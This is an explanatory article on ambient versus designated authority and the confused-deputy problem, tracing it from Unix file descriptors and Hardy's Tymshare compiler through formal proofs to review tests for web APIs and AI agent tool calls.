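# Ambient and explicitly designated authority in software and AI agents

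## What ambient and designated authority are

Access control is the part of a computer system that decides whether to carry out a program's request, such as reading a file, sending a message from a mailbox or deleting a row in a database. It can decide by looking up the user account the program runs under and checking what that account may do. Security researchers say that such a program exercises ambient authority, because its right to act comes from its surroundings and appears nowhere in the request. With designated authority, the program instead includes in its request something that both identifies the file and entitles the program to use it.

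Most computers use both arrangements, though usually only the identity check is called access control. According to Habitat Chronicles' *What Are Capabilities?* (2017), every mainstream desktop and phone operating system keeps a record of who may do what to each file. This works for a person editing their own document with a program they trust, and they never have to think about it. The choice between the two arrangements starts to matter when a program works for more than one party, or when an outsider can choose the name of the file it acts on.

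### The vocabulary

A subject is whatever makes a request. Miller and Shapiro, in *Paradigm Regained* (2003), define it as the smallest unit of computation to which a system can give a separate set of access rights. Depending on the system, that unit may be everything that runs under a user's account, a single running process, or, in some programming languages, a single object inside a program. A resource is whatever the request acts on, such as a file or a mailbox. It can also be another program, which can then make requests of its own.

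Authority is the ability of a subject to affect a resource, directly or through others. Miller and Shapiro distinguish it from permission, by which they mean direct access only. In their example, Alice has permission to read `/etc/passwd`, the file in which Unix systems list user accounts, and Bob does not. If Alice is willing to send Bob copies of the text, Bob has authority to read the file even though the system's records give him no permission. A reviewer who lists only permissions will therefore miss what a program can do by asking another program to act.

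Every request must indicate which resource it is about, and it does this with a designator. A name, such as a file path, account number, or record ID, is a designator that carries no authority to use the resource. For example, anyone can write down the path of a colleague's payroll file, but that doesn't give them permission to open it. A handle both designates a resource and carries the authority to use it.

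A capability is a handle that nobody can forge. (Here the word doesn't refer to what an AI model can do.) *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) calls it an "unforgeable ticket", which proves that whoever presents it may access the object it names. The ticket also specifies the kind of access, so a capability to read a file differs from a capability to write to it.

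A capability is unforgeable if a program cannot create one for something it could not already reach. File paths are forgeable because any program can compose any string. Habitat Chronicles compares C++ and Java. A C++ program can treat an arbitrary integer as a pointer to an object in memory, so pointers are forgeable. Java does not allow that conversion, and a Java program can use only object references that it created or that other code gave it.

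The last term is the access control list, a list kept with a resource that says which identities may do what to it. Miller, Yee and Shapiro, in *Capability Myths Demolished* (2003), illustrate it with a small table of three users and three files:

| | `/etc/passwd` | `/u/markm/foo` | `/etc/motd` |
|---|---|---|---|
| Alice | read | write | nothing |
| Bob | read | nothing | read |
| Carol | read | write | read |

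Each column of the table is an access control list: the list for `/u/markm/foo` gives Alice and Carol permission to write to it. Each row looks like a list of the capabilities that one user holds. The choice between access control lists and capabilities is more than bookkeeping, even though the table makes them look like the same information in a different order.

Miller, Yee and Shapiro argue that this is a mistake. One of their reasons is that an access control list, which is stored with the file and identifies users, gives a user no way to refer to the file. The system therefore needs a separate set of names, such as file paths. A capability is held by the user and identifies the file, so it can both refer to the file and grant access to it. The table shows who may do what, but not how a request specifies the file and the right it relies on. Ambient and designated authority differ in those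 two respects.

### Authority that nobody selects

Miller, Yee and Shapiro define ambient authority as authority that is "exercised, but not selected, by its user". They compare it to a world with doors but no keys, where a door opens by itself for anyone who is allowed in. The person entering has no way to specify which right they are using. In a world with locks, a person chooses both a door and a key, and gets in only if the key fits.

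Saving a document is an everyday example of ambient authority. When a user presses Save in Microsoft Word, Word requests that the operating system write to the document's file. The operating system checks that the user is allowed to write to that file but, as Habitat Chronicles points out, it cannot determine whether the user asked for this particular write. If Word encrypted every other file the user owns for ransom, each of those writes would pass the same check.

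Two of the oldest operations in Unix show the contrast. A program first calls `open()` to use a file. According to the Linux manual's *open(2)* page, the call takes a path and flags that specify, among other things, whether to open the file for reading, writing or both. The call has no parameter for a credential. The operating system identifies the account the program is running under, checks the file's permissions, and either opens the file or returns an error. Like the self-opening door, this is ambient authority, and Miller, Yee and Shapiro also use `open()` as their example.

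If the call succeeds, it returns a file descriptor, a small whole number that indexes the system's table of the files this process has open. To get the contents, the program then calls `read()`, which, according to the Linux manual's *read(2)* page, takes the descriptor, a place in memory to put the data, and the number of bytes wanted. It does not take a path, and the system ordinarily does not check again who is running the program. `read()` fails if the number does not correspond to an open file or if the program opened the file only for writing.

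So a descriptor is a handle, although it looks like a bare number. A program can pass any number in a call, but the number can refer only to an entry in that program's own table, and the call returns an error if there is no such entry. A descriptor is also more stable than a path. Once a program has opened a file, the descriptor keeps referring to that file even if someone deletes the path or makes it lead to a different file.

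The `open()` and `read()` calls give a simplified picture of the distinction. `open()` uses ambient authority to turn a name into a handle, and `read()` uses the handle. On some network file systems, however, the server checks identity again at each read, and according to the Linux manual, `open()` may succeed there and `read()` still fail. Miller, Yee and Shapiro also call descriptors nearly but not quite equivalent to the capabilities of a pure capability system, because an access control list governs the channel through which one process sends a descriptor to another.

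### How much authority a copy command needs

It might seem to make little difference whether a program receives a name and opens the file itself, or receives the file already open. Miller, Tulloh and Shapiro (2005), in *The Structure of Authority*, show with two Unix commands that it makes a large one. Both commands copy the contents of `foo.txt` into `bar.txt`. The first is:

`cp foo.txt bar.txt`

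The shell, the program that reads what the user types, starts `cp` and passes it only two strings, "foo.txt" and "bar.txt". To find and open the files these strings refer to, `cp` has to use the user's whole collection of file names, and it must already have the right to read and write any file the user might mention. Called this way, `cp` needs the user's entire authority over the file system, even though the user meant only two files.

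The second command gets the same result by a different route:

`cat < foo.txt > bar.txt`

The angle brackets tell the shell to open `foo.txt` for reading and `bar.txt` for writing, and to start `cat` with those files as its input and output. A new process inherits its parent's open descriptors, so `cat` starts with both files already open. The shell doesn't pass it the file names. `cat` reads from one descriptor and writes to the other until the input ends.

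The user still types file names in the second command, but a different program looks them up. With `cat`, the shell does the lookup, and the shell acts for the user and has good reason to have access to all of the user's files. With `cp`, the copying program does the lookup, so it needs the authority to look up any of those files. Miller and Shapiro compare `cat` to an ordinary function call in a programming language, in which the caller works out what its own names refer to and passes those things to the function.

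On an ordinary Unix machine, `cat` is no safer than `cp`, because both run with all of the user's authority. If an attacker had tampered with `cat`, it could ignore its two descriptors, call `open()` on the user's private letters and copy those instead. The programs differ in the least authority they need. Without the ability to open files by name, `cat` could still make this copy, but `cp` could not copy anything.

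An interface designer's choice between names and handles affects how much authority a program needs. A program that accepts names needs enough authority to use any resource that might be named. If it accepts handles instead, it needs no standing authority over the resources in its requests, because each request includes the authority it requires. The program may still have surplus authority unless someone removes it, which Unix does not do by default. Miller, Tulloh and Shapiro find it ironic that in systems that grant access in both ways, only the per-user checks are presented as access control.

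### The compiler that wrote over the bills

Excess authority can cause harm even when the program that holds it is neither malicious nor broken, as in the case that made the distinction matter. In *The Confused Deputy* (1988), Hardy tells what he calls "a nearly true story" from Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Tymshare's compiler was in a directory called SYSX, and a user who ran it could name a file to receive debugging output. The company also wanted the compiler to record statistics in a file in SYSX, so it gave the compiler a licence to write to any file in that directory, which also held the billing records. One user learned the name of the billing file and gave it to the compiler as the destination for the debugging output. Because the compiler had its licence, the operating system allowed the write, and the billing information was lost.

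In Hardy's account, the compiler had no reason to use the billing file. It could reach the file only because its licence covered a whole directory, though its task required only one other file. Later versions often simplify the story by having the compiler itself keep the bills.

Hardy does not blame the code that wrote the debugging output, which was correct when written and became wrong, unchanged, when someone later granted the licence. He attributes the problem to the compiler having authority from two sources. The user who ran it gave it authority for the user's output, and the company gave it authority for the statistics. When the compiler asked to open a file, it could not specify which authority to use. Hardy called such a program a confused deputy: a program led to use its own authority for a requester who lacks that authority. His remedy was to give the compiler one capability for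 the statistics file and have the user supply another for the debugging output. A user with no right to write to the billing file could not have supplied a capability for it.

Miller, Yee and Shapiro analyse this case in terms of two properties that a system may have or lack:

- No ambient authority: a subject must select the authority it uses each time it accesses a resource.
- No designation without authority: designating a resource always conveys the authority to use it.

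An interface with the second property accepts only handles, never bare names. Standard Unix file permissions have neither property, and open file descriptors have both. Locks and keys have only the first. A visitor has to choose a key, so no authority is ambient, but anyone can point at a door without owning its key. An interface cannot have the second property without the first, because every request has to designate its resource somehow.

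### Agents, harnesses and tool calls

The same distinction now comes up in systems built on language models, which are programs that take in text and produce text. A model cannot open a file or send a message without an ordinary program around it, which most developers call the harness. Hugging Face's glossary *Harness, Scaffold, and the AI Agent Terms Worth Getting Right* (2026) defines an agent as the model and harness together. It also warns that usage is unsettled and that some products call everything except the model a harness.

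An agent works in a loop. The harness sends the model its instructions, the user's request and descriptions of the available functions, called tools. To use a tool, the model writes a tool call, which is structured text that names a function and gives its arguments. For example, a call might name a function that sends email and give an address and a message as its arguments. The harness reads the call, runs the function, adds the result to the text the model will see next, and calls the model again. The loop repeats until the harness ends it. The model only writes the request, and the harness, which holds the credentials, carries it out.

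The arguments of a tool call are designators, and because a model produces text, they are typically names, such as an email address, a file path or a customer number. It may be hard to tell who or what chose a name. In Hardy's story, a user typed the file name that caused the damage directly into the command. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) describes how, in an agent, planning steps, retrieved documents, earlier tool outputs and arguments that the model itself generated may all come between the original request and the action.

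Writers on agent security use the older term somewhat loosely. *AgentCap* (2026), which presents a system for authorising agents' actions at runtime, includes a small constructed scenario in which a task requires four capabilities. The system issues only those four and still permits every legitimate action, whereas the baseline, labelled "ambient authority", grants all eight that exist. That comparison measures how much authority the agent holds, but ambient authority in the 2003 sense concerns whether a request selects the authority it uses. An agent with only four rights still exercises them ambiently if the harness applies whichever one fits the name in the tool call.

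## What the rule of no designation without authority guarantees

Under the rule of no designation without authority, an interface accepts only handles. Capability researchers recommend this rule because it prevents ambient authority and protects programs from becoming confused deputies. A short deduction shows that it prevents ambient authority. It protects only partially against confused deputies, and in 2016 three researchers proved the limits of that protection.

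### Four models of access

Miller and colleagues arrived at the rule by comparing four models that writers on security had often run together.

In the model called "access lists as columns", each file's column in the table of users and files is its access list. Requests have to refer to files by separate names, which carry no authority, so no access-list system can follow the rule.

The capabilities-as-rows model uses the same table but organizes it by row, so each subject has a list of what it may use. The model doesn't specify how a request refers to a resource, or require the subject to pick an entry from its list. The operating system can therefore consult the list on the subject's behalf, in which case the authority is as ambient as before. "POSIX capabilities", a Unix mechanism, work this way despite their name. They are a fixed set of flags attached to a process, and one of them, `CAP_CHOWN`,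 lets the process change the owner of any file on the machine.

In the model of capabilities as keys, a subject must choose a key (its authority) as well as a door (the resource). Miller and colleagues give SPKI, a scheme of signed certificates, as a real example. A program must present a certificate to get access, so it selects the authority it uses. But the certificate contains the resource's name in readable text, so anyone can copy that name into a request that doesn't include the certificate.

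In the object-capability model, a program refers to a resource through a reference it holds, and that reference is also the permission to use the resource. Nearly all the systems that people have built and called "capability systems" follow this model.

| Model | Does designating a resource always convey authority over it? | Must the subject select the authority it uses? |
|---|---|---|
| Access lists as columns | no, and it cannot | no |
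| Capabilities as rows | unspecified | no |
| Capabilities as keys | no | yes |
| Object capabilities | yes | yes |

### Why the rule implies selection, and why selection is not enough

No model in the table has "yes" in the middle column and "no" on the right, and none could. Every request has to designate its resource, and under the rule the designator carries the authority to use it. By choosing the designator, the requester therefore also selects the authority, which means that the authority is not ambient. (A designer could add the rule to the rows model, but the authority in it would then stop being ambient too.)

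The converse does not hold, as the keys model shows. The gap matters in practice because of how a person picks a key, which Miller and colleagues say the analogy usually leaves out. A careful person decides which key to use before going to the door, while someone else tries every key on the ring. Both select an authority, in the sense that one particular key turns the lock.

Hardy's compiler overwrote the billing file when a user named it as the destination for debugging output. Suppose the compiler had held two keys, one from the company and one from the user, and the user again named the billing file. The compiler tries the user's key, which fails. If it then tries the company's key, that key works and the compiler overwrites the billing records again. A client library that responds to "permission denied" by retrying with the next stored credential has the same flaw.

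To be safe, the compiler has to keep track of what each key is for. Miller and colleagues suggest imagining that a program labels each key with its purpose when it receives it. The program can do this only if it can interpret the context in which the key arrived, so it can't label keys that are added to its ring without notice. The rule makes labeling easier because each authority arrives in the request it is meant to be used for.

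### Switching hats

Tymshare, the company in the story, tried an intermediate design. Hardy describes a new system call to "switch hats" that let a program choose between its own licence and the authority of the user who had started it. If the compiler tried to open the billing file under the user's authority, the system would correctly refuse.

The call let the compiler select which authority to use, but the file name still arrived separately, as a string with no authority attached. At every place where the compiler opened a file, its programmer had to know whose file name it was about to use and select the matching authority. Forgetting once would bring back the original fault. Like the keys model, the design therefore removes ambient authority without following the rule.

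Hardy reports that some applications soon needed more than two authorities, though he doesn't say which. Suppose, for example, that a build service runs the compiler for its customers. The output file belongs to the customer, the build log to the service, and the statistics file to whoever maintains the compiler. The authority of whoever started the compiler is the build service's, which presumably covers every customer's files, so the compiler needs a third authority for the customer. Each further party requires another authority, and the compiler must record which file name came from whom. Tymshare's system also had kinds of authority unrelated to files. Hardy found no obvious way to generalise the call to cover them, and the changes spread through the system. When he last wrote down the conditions for a program to open a file, they took fourteen "ands" and "ors".

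He also considers having the compiler inspect the file name, but rejects this. Users have good reasons to send output to other directories, some may have legitimate access to the directory with the billing file, and that directory held other sensitive files too. With handles, the build service needs no such checks and no extra hats. The compiler receives separate handles for the output, the log and the statistics, and writes to each in the same way.

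*ACLs Don't* (Close, 2009) argues that the access-list model cannot make correct decisions when an interaction has more than two parties, because the information it would need is lost from one message to the next. Cross-site request forgery exploits this loss. A hostile web page makes a visitor's browser send a request to the visitor's bank, and the bank sees the visitor's credentials but not who prompted the request. In a message to a web-standards mailing list, Close traced the risk to the ordinary step of taking an identifier from one party's response and putting it into a request to another.

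### How far the informal argument goes

The 2003 paper makes a more limited claim about confused deputies than its reputation suggests. Miller and colleagues say that one common kind, in which a malicious party designates a resource it is not supposed to access, "simply cannot occur" where designation and authority are inseparable. They add that no security model can prevent people from writing bad programs. Their summary table rates systems that follow the rule "best" against confused deputies, but only in comparison with other systems.

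In *Confused deputy*, Karp (2026) asked a mailing list of capability researchers whether anyone had proved that the vulnerability is impossible to express in a capability system. William Leslie replied that it can be expressed, because a deputy can put its own capabilities in a map and let the client choose one. If the client chooses by sending a string or a number, that value is a name, and the deputy has Hardy's problem again, even though it runs on a capability system.

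Miller replied that the 2003 argument was "precise but non-formal". Roughly, it covers deputies that designate everything by capability. He called this a severe restriction that many normal deputies don't meet, even in capability systems, though he thinks most of them are still safe. His rule of thumb is that a deputy is probably not vulnerable if it avoids rights amplification, which means combining two capabilities to get authority that neither conveys alone.

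### A definition of the attack

A proof needs a definition of a confused-deputy attack. Rajani, Garg and Rezk (2016) gave what they believe was the first formal one in *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks*, using a very small programming language they designed for the purpose.

In this language, every memory location has an owner, and owners are ordered by trust. A program is a sequence of blocks, each of which runs on behalf of a principal (a user or a piece of code). A block may write to a location only if its principal ranks at least as high as the location's owner. One block is blank, and the attacker can fill it with any code.

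The same program can run under different enforcement rules. Under the access-control rules, the system checks the policy when code writes. Under the capability rules, it checks earlier, whenever code obtains a reference that permits writing, and halts the program if the code's principal may not write there. Rajani and colleagues model the rule of no designation without authority this way, so code never holds a write reference that it lacks the authority to use.

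These two regimes are not equivalent. Suppose a block may write to location A but not to location B, and it stores a reference to B in A. The access-control rules let it run because nothing writes to B, but the capability rules halt it because it has obtained a reference to B. Rajani and colleagues proved that access control permits every step that capabilities permit, and this example shows that it also permits others. They also proved that under both regimes, no block ever writes to a location the policy forbids it to write to.

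Hardy's compiler did not break a check of this kind either, since it was entitled to write to the billing file. So the definition has to look at the outcome. The attacker has a set of locations that it would like to change. A program is free from confused-deputy attacks if, whatever code the attacker puts in the blank, at least one of two conditions holds for each of those locations when the program finishes:

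- **No adversary control.** The location would have ended up with the same value whatever other code the attacker had supplied.
- **Direct adversary write.** The attacker's block, running by itself, could have written that final value to the location.

An attacker who misuses a deputy must have some control over the value and be unable to write that value without the deputy.

Taken strictly, this definition rules out some useful programs. For example, a compiler that charges by the size of the source file is meant to let users influence their bills. Rajani and colleagues therefore let the programmer mark a block as endorsed to declare that it acts on the attacker's input on purpose. The revised definition applies only to stretches of the program that contain no endorsed block.

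### Explicit and implicit designation

Their first example is a stripped-down version of the compiler. In simplified notation, its single instruction is:

`location in OUTPUT := compile(SOURCE)`

The attacker can write to both `OUTPUT` and `SOURCE`. It sets `OUTPUT` to refer to a protected location, and the compiler writes the compiled program there. Access control allows this because the compiler has the highest rank and may write anywhere. Both conditions fail, because the result varies with the attacker's source code and the attacker could not have written it to the protected location directly.

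The capability rules stop the attack before the compiler runs. To put the reference in `OUTPUT`, the attacker's own code must first obtain it, and the system halts the program at that point. The attacker can supply only references to locations it could already write to, so the condition of direct adversary write always holds.

Now suppose that the attacker supplies only a value:

`PROTECTED := INBOX`

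The attacker can write to `INBOX` but not to `PROTECTED`. The deputy copies the attacker's value from `INBOX` into `PROTECTED`, so `PROTECTED` holds 42 if the attacker writes 42 and 41 if it writes 41. By the definition, this is a confused-deputy attack. The capability rules allow it because the attacker never touches a reference to `PROTECTED`. That reference is part of the deputy's own code, and the deputy is entitled to it. Rajani and colleagues compare the program to a web server open to SQL injection, where a visitor's text alters a database that the visitor cannot reach directly.

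In the third example, the deputy doesn't even copy anything from the attacker:

`if FLAG then PROTECTED := 41 else PROTECTED := 42`

The deputy's programmer wrote both numbers as constants, but the attacker can choose which one ends up in `PROTECTED` by setting `FLAG` to true or false. Again, there is no reference for the capability rules to intercept.

A fourth program is vulnerable because, before it starts, a memory location that the attacker can write to already contains a reference to a protected location. The deputy follows that reference and writes the attacker's chosen value to the protected location.

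Rajani and colleagues call the compiler's case explicit designation, because the attacker gives the deputy the write reference. They call the other cases implicit designation, because the deputy already has the reference and the attacker influences what it writes with it. The rule prevents only attacks that use explicit designation.

Not everyone would count the implicit cases as confused deputies. In the exchange with Leslie and Miller, Karp defined a confused deputy as one that "uses its permissions on a resource designated by somebody else", and by that definition the copying program merely trusts bad input. The same disagreement had come up a year earlier over an example in *Is this a confused deputy?* (Karp 2025). In the example, Alice keeps one file for each letter of the alphabet and adds every word to the files for the letters it contains. Bob's service tells her which files to update.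 If Bob is malicious, he can name an unrelated file of hers, and she will overwrite it. Karp's solution is to give Bob a capability for each word file and have him send back the ones for the files he chooses.

Mike Stay objected that Bob could still break Alice's filing system, for example by choosing the file for Z when the word is "cat". To prevent that, the capability would have to check that the choice follows her rule about letters, as well as designate a file. Karp replied that whether Bob's answers are correct is a different issue from whether he can make Alice write to a file she doesn't want written. That distinction is fair, but it shows how little the rule covers. If Alice needs each word to go in the correct file, she also needs Stay's check.

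### When capabilities are sufficient

Rajani and colleagues also worked out when the capability rules stop every attack that their definition covers. A trusted block can come to hold a write reference to a protected location in three ways: its programmer wrote the reference into the code, the block reads it from memory, or the attacker passes it in. The capability rules close off the last of these. Their Theorem 4 says that a program is free from confused-deputy attacks under the capability rules if two conditions close off the others:

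- No trusted block, other than an endorsed one, has in its code a write reference to a location in the attacker's target set that the attacker cannot write to itself.
- No location in memory contains such a reference when the program starts.

The proof is short, and it shows why the theorem is of little use. Under these conditions, no unendorsed block ever obtains a reference to a protected target, so none of them writes to one, and the attacker has no control over values that nobody changes. But a deputy's purpose is to use its special authority on behalf of others. By the paper's own account, these restrictions "render the language useless for almost all practical purposes".

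Even Hardy's proposed remedy fails the conditions. His compiler would hold a capability for the statistics file, but the user would influence what it writes there, because the statistics record which language features the user's program contains. If the programmer endorses the block that writes the statistics, the theorem applies to the rest of the program, but only because the definition no longer covers the block where the influence occurs.

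### Tracking where values came from

Rajani and colleagues instead propose provenance tracking, in which the system records whose data went into each value. It labels every value with a principal that ranks no higher than the owner of any location read in computing it. A constant gets the highest label. When an unendorsed block writes to a location, the system halts the program unless the labels on the value and on the reference to the location both rank at least as high as the location's owner.

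This stops the program that copies `INBOX` into `PROTECTED`, because the value has a low label. It also stops the attack through a reference left in memory, because the reference came from a place the attacker can write to. It does not stop the program that branches on `FLAG`, because the values there are the deputy's own constants.

The full version of the scheme catches that program by keeping one more label, for the current point in the program. When execution enters the body of an `if` or a loop, the system lowers this label to account for the data in the condition, and it restores the earlier label when execution leaves the body. Every write must also pass a check against this label. After branching on `FLAG`, the deputy cannot write to `PROTECTED` until the branch ends. Theorem 6 states that full tracking prevents all confused-deputy attacks, for any program and any initial memory.

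The table shows the results for five of the programs. "No guarantee" means the program does not meet the conditions under which the mechanism has been proved sufficient.

| Program | Access control | Capabilities | Tracking of values only | Full tracking |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Attacker supplies the location | attack succeeds | stopped | stopped | stopped |
| Attacker supplies the value | attack succeeds | no guarantee | stopped | stopped |
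| Attacker influences a branch | attack succeeds | no guarantee | no guarantee | stopped |
| Reference already in memory | attack succeeds | no guarantee | stopped | stopped |
| Harmless copy from a less trusted location to a more trusted one, with no attacker present | runs | runs | stopped | stopped |

The last row shows the drawbacks of tracking. It enforces a stronger property than the definition requires, that less trusted data never influences more trusted locations, and many legitimate programs violate that property. The programmer can endorse the blocks that do, but provenance checks don't apply inside endorsed blocks, so those blocks lose the protection. Full tracking also adds more run-time overhead than tracking values alone.

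Gallo (2026) points out in *Full Provenance on the COSS Causal Axis* that "unconditionally" in Theorem 6 is relative to the small language in which the theorem is stated. Gallo's preprint offers a proof for systems in general, in which authority can only shrink as one event causes another. The proof assumes that the system faithfully records every path by which a request leads to a protected effect, which whoever builds the system must ensure.

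*Type-Confusion Security* (Ren, Chen and colleagues, 2026) applies related ideas to programs that call functions on machines they don't control. In its main example, a currency exchange asks each customer for a function to collect payment with. An attacker supplies the exchange's own payout function, so the exchange pays out when it should collect. Anyone can refer to any function in this setting, so a function reference is only a name. The defence treats any call made through a reference from outside as untrusted. The payout function accepts only trusted calls, so it rejects this one when the program runs. An attacker could use the same substitution to make a program that runs tools for an AI application act without the user's approval.

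Ren and colleagues give a machine-checked proof that a program that passes their type checker is free of confused-deputy attacks, even if the attacker ignores the types. Their definition of such an attack is narrower than the one from 2016, because it concerns who may call a function and not what value ends up in memory. The programmer also has to annotate the honest code with trust levels, which the rule alone doesn't require.

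### What a designer can claim

Suppose a report service accepts a handle for the output file, a title, and an option to delete old reports. It also keeps two handles of its own, one for an activity log and one for the archive of old reports.

Because the client passes the output file as a handle, the designer can claim that no client can make the service write a report over a file that the client had no authority to write to. This claim depends on handles being unforgeable and on nobody having given the client one it shouldn't have. It survives changes elsewhere, including the kind that broke Hardy's compiler. If an administrator later gives the service access to more files, no client can reach them through the output parameter.

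The guarantee doesn't cover the title or the delete option. If the service copies the title into its log, clients influence what the log contains, and the delete option determines whether the service uses its authority over the archive to delete things. The designer has to validate these inputs or track their influence, or else state openly that clients are meant to have this influence and manually review the code that grants it. If the service also accepts a report number and looks up the matching handle in its own table, the number is a name, so a client can ask for somebody else's report and the output handle won't prevent it.

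The claim also covers only writing and does not guarantee secrecy. The language that Rajani and colleagues studied protects locations from being overwritten but lets code use any read reference it holds. Karp argued that a party who already has a capability for a file gains nothing by tricking a deputy into writing to it, except that the deputy might write something the party should not know. The report service could follow the rule at every step and still put one customer's figures into a file that another customer supplied.

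## How to tell which kind of authority an interface uses

A reviewer can tell whether a parameter is a name or a handle better by testing the interface than by relying on labels. A file descriptor looks like an ordinary number, and "POSIX capabilities" are ambient despite their name. The three tests are to select an authority, substitute a designator, and transfer the message to another sender. Any one of these tests can mislead without the others.

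Suppose a web service shows customers their invoices. The customer's browser sends an invoice number, and the service queries a database for it. The customer is the requester, the service is the calling program, and the database grants or refuses access. The reviewer should write down who fills each role before starting, because one credential can give different results at different points in the chain. After a redesign, the reviewer repeats the same tests at the same points.

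### Selection

The selection test checks whether the calling code can specify which of its authorities to use. The reviewer gives the program two authorities, only one of which covers the resource, and tries to make the program request the resource with the other. In the invoice service, these could be two database logins, one of which cannot read invoices. If the call cannot specify an authority, or if the request succeeds anyway, the system is choosing the authority, so the authority is ambient.

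If the request fails, the program's choice of authority affects the outcome, but that choice may be very coarse. A service that holds one login for all invoices passes the test because it selects that login, but it cannot specify that an invoice should be read only if customer A may read it.

### Substitution

In the substitution test, the requester substitutes the name of something it isn't allowed to access, and the reviewer checks whether the request succeeds on the program's own authority. Web testers do this routinely. *Testing for Insecure Direct Object References*, a guide from the security non-profit OWASP, describes how attackers reach other users' database records or files by changing a parameter that points to an object. Y-Security's 2024 copy of the guide recommends testing with at least two users who own different objects, so that the tester has real identifiers to try and doesn't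 have to guess them. For the invoice service, the tester logs in as customer A and requests one of customer B's invoices.

If the service returns the invoice, the parameter is only a name and the service is a confused deputy. OWASP's *Authorisation of direct object references* gives the example of an internet bank that uses account numbers as database keys and puts them in its web pages. Unless the bank also checks that the user holds the account, an attacker can see or alter any account by changing the number. An Australian Taxation Office site was attacked this way in 2000. The fault is still common. OWASP ranked it as the most critical risk to web APIs in both 2019 and 2023, according to Auth0's *how fine grained authorization solves critical api security risk*.

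A refusal is harder to interpret because it can have two causes that look the same from outside. Customer A may have had no way to produce a valid designator for B's invoice. Or the service may have looked up the invoice's owner, seen that it was not A, and returned an error. In that case the invoice number is still a name, and customers are safe only as long as programmers remember to write the ownership check for every new operation. The reviewer can tell the two cases apart by reading the code, or by removing the ownership check from a test copy and repeating the request, which will still fail if the parameter is a handle.

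### Transfer

In the transfer test, the reviewer has another process, with no standing rights, send the complete message. If the request still succeeds, the message carries all the authority it uses. That makes delegation easy, but anyone who finds the message in a log gets the authority too.

If the message fails, the system relied on something outside the message. Often this is the account the sender runs under, in which case the authority is probably ambient. It could also be a private key that only the original sender holds, or a rule that requests must come from a particular network, and neither makes the authority ambient.

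The reviewer also has to use a channel that can carry the handles in the message. A process that only reuses the number of another process's open descriptor gets an error or an unrelated file. Sending the descriptor itself through a socket, which Unix allows, counts as a successful transfer because the receiver can then use the file even if it could never have opened it.

### Six common interfaces

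The table applies the tests to six ways of making a request. An API key is a secret string that a service issues to a program. OAuth is a standard that lets a user authorise a program to use their account at another service. OAuth scopes are named sets of permissions, such as "read invoices". A pre-signed URL is a web address that includes a signature authorising one particular request. The substitution column assumes that nobody has added an ownership check.

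| Interface | Can the caller select an authority? | Does a forbidden name succeed? | Does the message work for another sender? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Path and user ID | no | yes, if the program's account may use the file | no |
| Open descriptor | yes, for one open file | no | yes, if the system passes the descriptor itself |
| API key and record ID | yes, but one key covers many records | yes, for any record the key covers | yes |
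| OAuth token with scopes and record ID | yes, down to the token's scopes | yes, within those scopes | yes, if whoever holds the token may use it |
| Pre-signed URL | yes, for one object and operation | no | yes, until it expires |
| SPKI certificate | yes | depends on who supplies the certificate | not without the private key |

The path relies on ambient authority, while the descriptor and the pre-signed URL are handles. The API key and the OAuth token fall in between. The program selects which credential to use, so that authority isn't ambient, but the record ID sent with the credential is a name. An OAuth scope such as "read invoices" can stop a program that only needs to read invoices from deleting them, but it doesn't stop the program from reading the wrong invoice.

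If a credential covers only one stored object and one action, substituting another object's name fails, even though the name is still a separate string. Developers can restrict temporary credentials this way, according to *Overview of presigned URLs* from AWS, Amazon's cloud-computing business, although limits on how fast AWS issues credentials can make this hard at scale.

According to AWS's *Download and upload objects with presigned URLs*, a program makes a pre-signed URL by specifying the storage bucket, the object's name, the operation and an expiry time. The signature covers all of these, so changing the object's name invalidates it. AWS calls the URLs "bearer tokens that grant access to those who possess them". When a request arrives, AWS checks the permissions of whoever signed the URL, so the URL stops working if the signer has lost the right to read the object. A reviewer might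 mistake this check for a sign of ambient authority, but it doesn't depend on who sent the request.

The reviewer also has to test the program that creates the URLs. Suppose the invoice service uses its own credentials to sign a URL for any object name a customer sends. Customer A can then request and receive a valid URL for customer B's invoice. The invoice service therefore fails the substitution test, even though the storage service passes it.

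SPKI is harder to classify because the resource's name can be separated from the certificate. Substitution succeeds if a program takes a name from a requester and searches its own certificates for a match, but fails if the requester has to provide the certificate. Even then, as Miller and colleagues point out, SPKI has no specific way to bind a certificate securely to the message it arrived with.

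An SPKI certificate grants its authority to a particular public key, so a copy is no use to someone without the matching private key (Ellison 1999, *SPKI Certificate Theory*). The holder can pass the authority on by signing a further certificate for somebody else's key, but only if the first certificate's delegation flag is set to true. The second certificate can convey no more authority than the first one allowed. Miller and colleagues also describe the spread of SPKI certificates as unrestricted, because a holder may give copies to anyone, but the transfer test shows that this description needs qualifying.

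Some of SPKI's designers opposed any such flag, arguing that a holder who may not delegate can still lend out the private key or run a service that signs other people's requests. The group adopted the flag anyway, assuming that people value their private keys too much to lend them. The objection also applies to the transfer test, which shows whether a message works for another sender but not whether its original sender will act for others.

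### Tokens that a library attaches

The case most likely to mislead a reviewer is a token that is explicit at one end of a connection and ambient at the other. Suppose the invoice service calls an outside accounting system through a client library. The programmer writes:

`invoices.delete(4821)`

The library reads a token from the service's configuration and adds it to the request. The token is therefore ambient to the code that called `delete`, which passed only a record ID and would have used the same token whether that ID came from an administrator or from a hostile customer. A reviewer who examines the network traffic will wrongly conclude that the caller selected its authority, because the accounting system receives both a token and a record ID.

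Both readings are correct, each for its own point in the chain. The reviewer should give more weight to the point where the program first uses its own credential with a name the requester supplied, since that is where confusion can happen. In this example, that point is the call to `delete`. Programs that carry out language models' tool calls often attach credentials in the same way.

The service could instead create a separate client for each customer, using a token that the customer has authorised:

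`customer_client.delete(4821)`

The code now selects an authority by choosing the client. The invoice number is still a name, but if customer A supplies the number of customer B's invoice, the accounting system refuses the request because A's token doesn't cover that invoice. This protection fails if the code picks the wrong client or retries a refused request with an administrator's client.

### Counting needed and reachable authority

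The tests show whether a requester can misdirect a program, but not how much damage the program could do if an attacker took it over completely. To assess that damage, the reviewer can count pairs of a resource and an operation, such as "read `report.docx`", and compare those the program can reach with those the task needs.

A hypothetical document converter works on a store of 50,000 files. A user asks it to convert `report.docx` and write the result to `report.pdf`, an existing file in the store. The task needs two permissions, one to read the first file and one to write to the second. If the converter runs under an account that can read and write every file, it has 100,000 permissions, 50,000 times as many as it needs.

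Suppose an administrator divides the store into 40,000 source files, which the converter may only read, and 10,000 output files, which it may only write. The converter can reach 40,000 + 10,000 = 50,000 pairs, which is half the previous total but still 25,000 times what the task needs.

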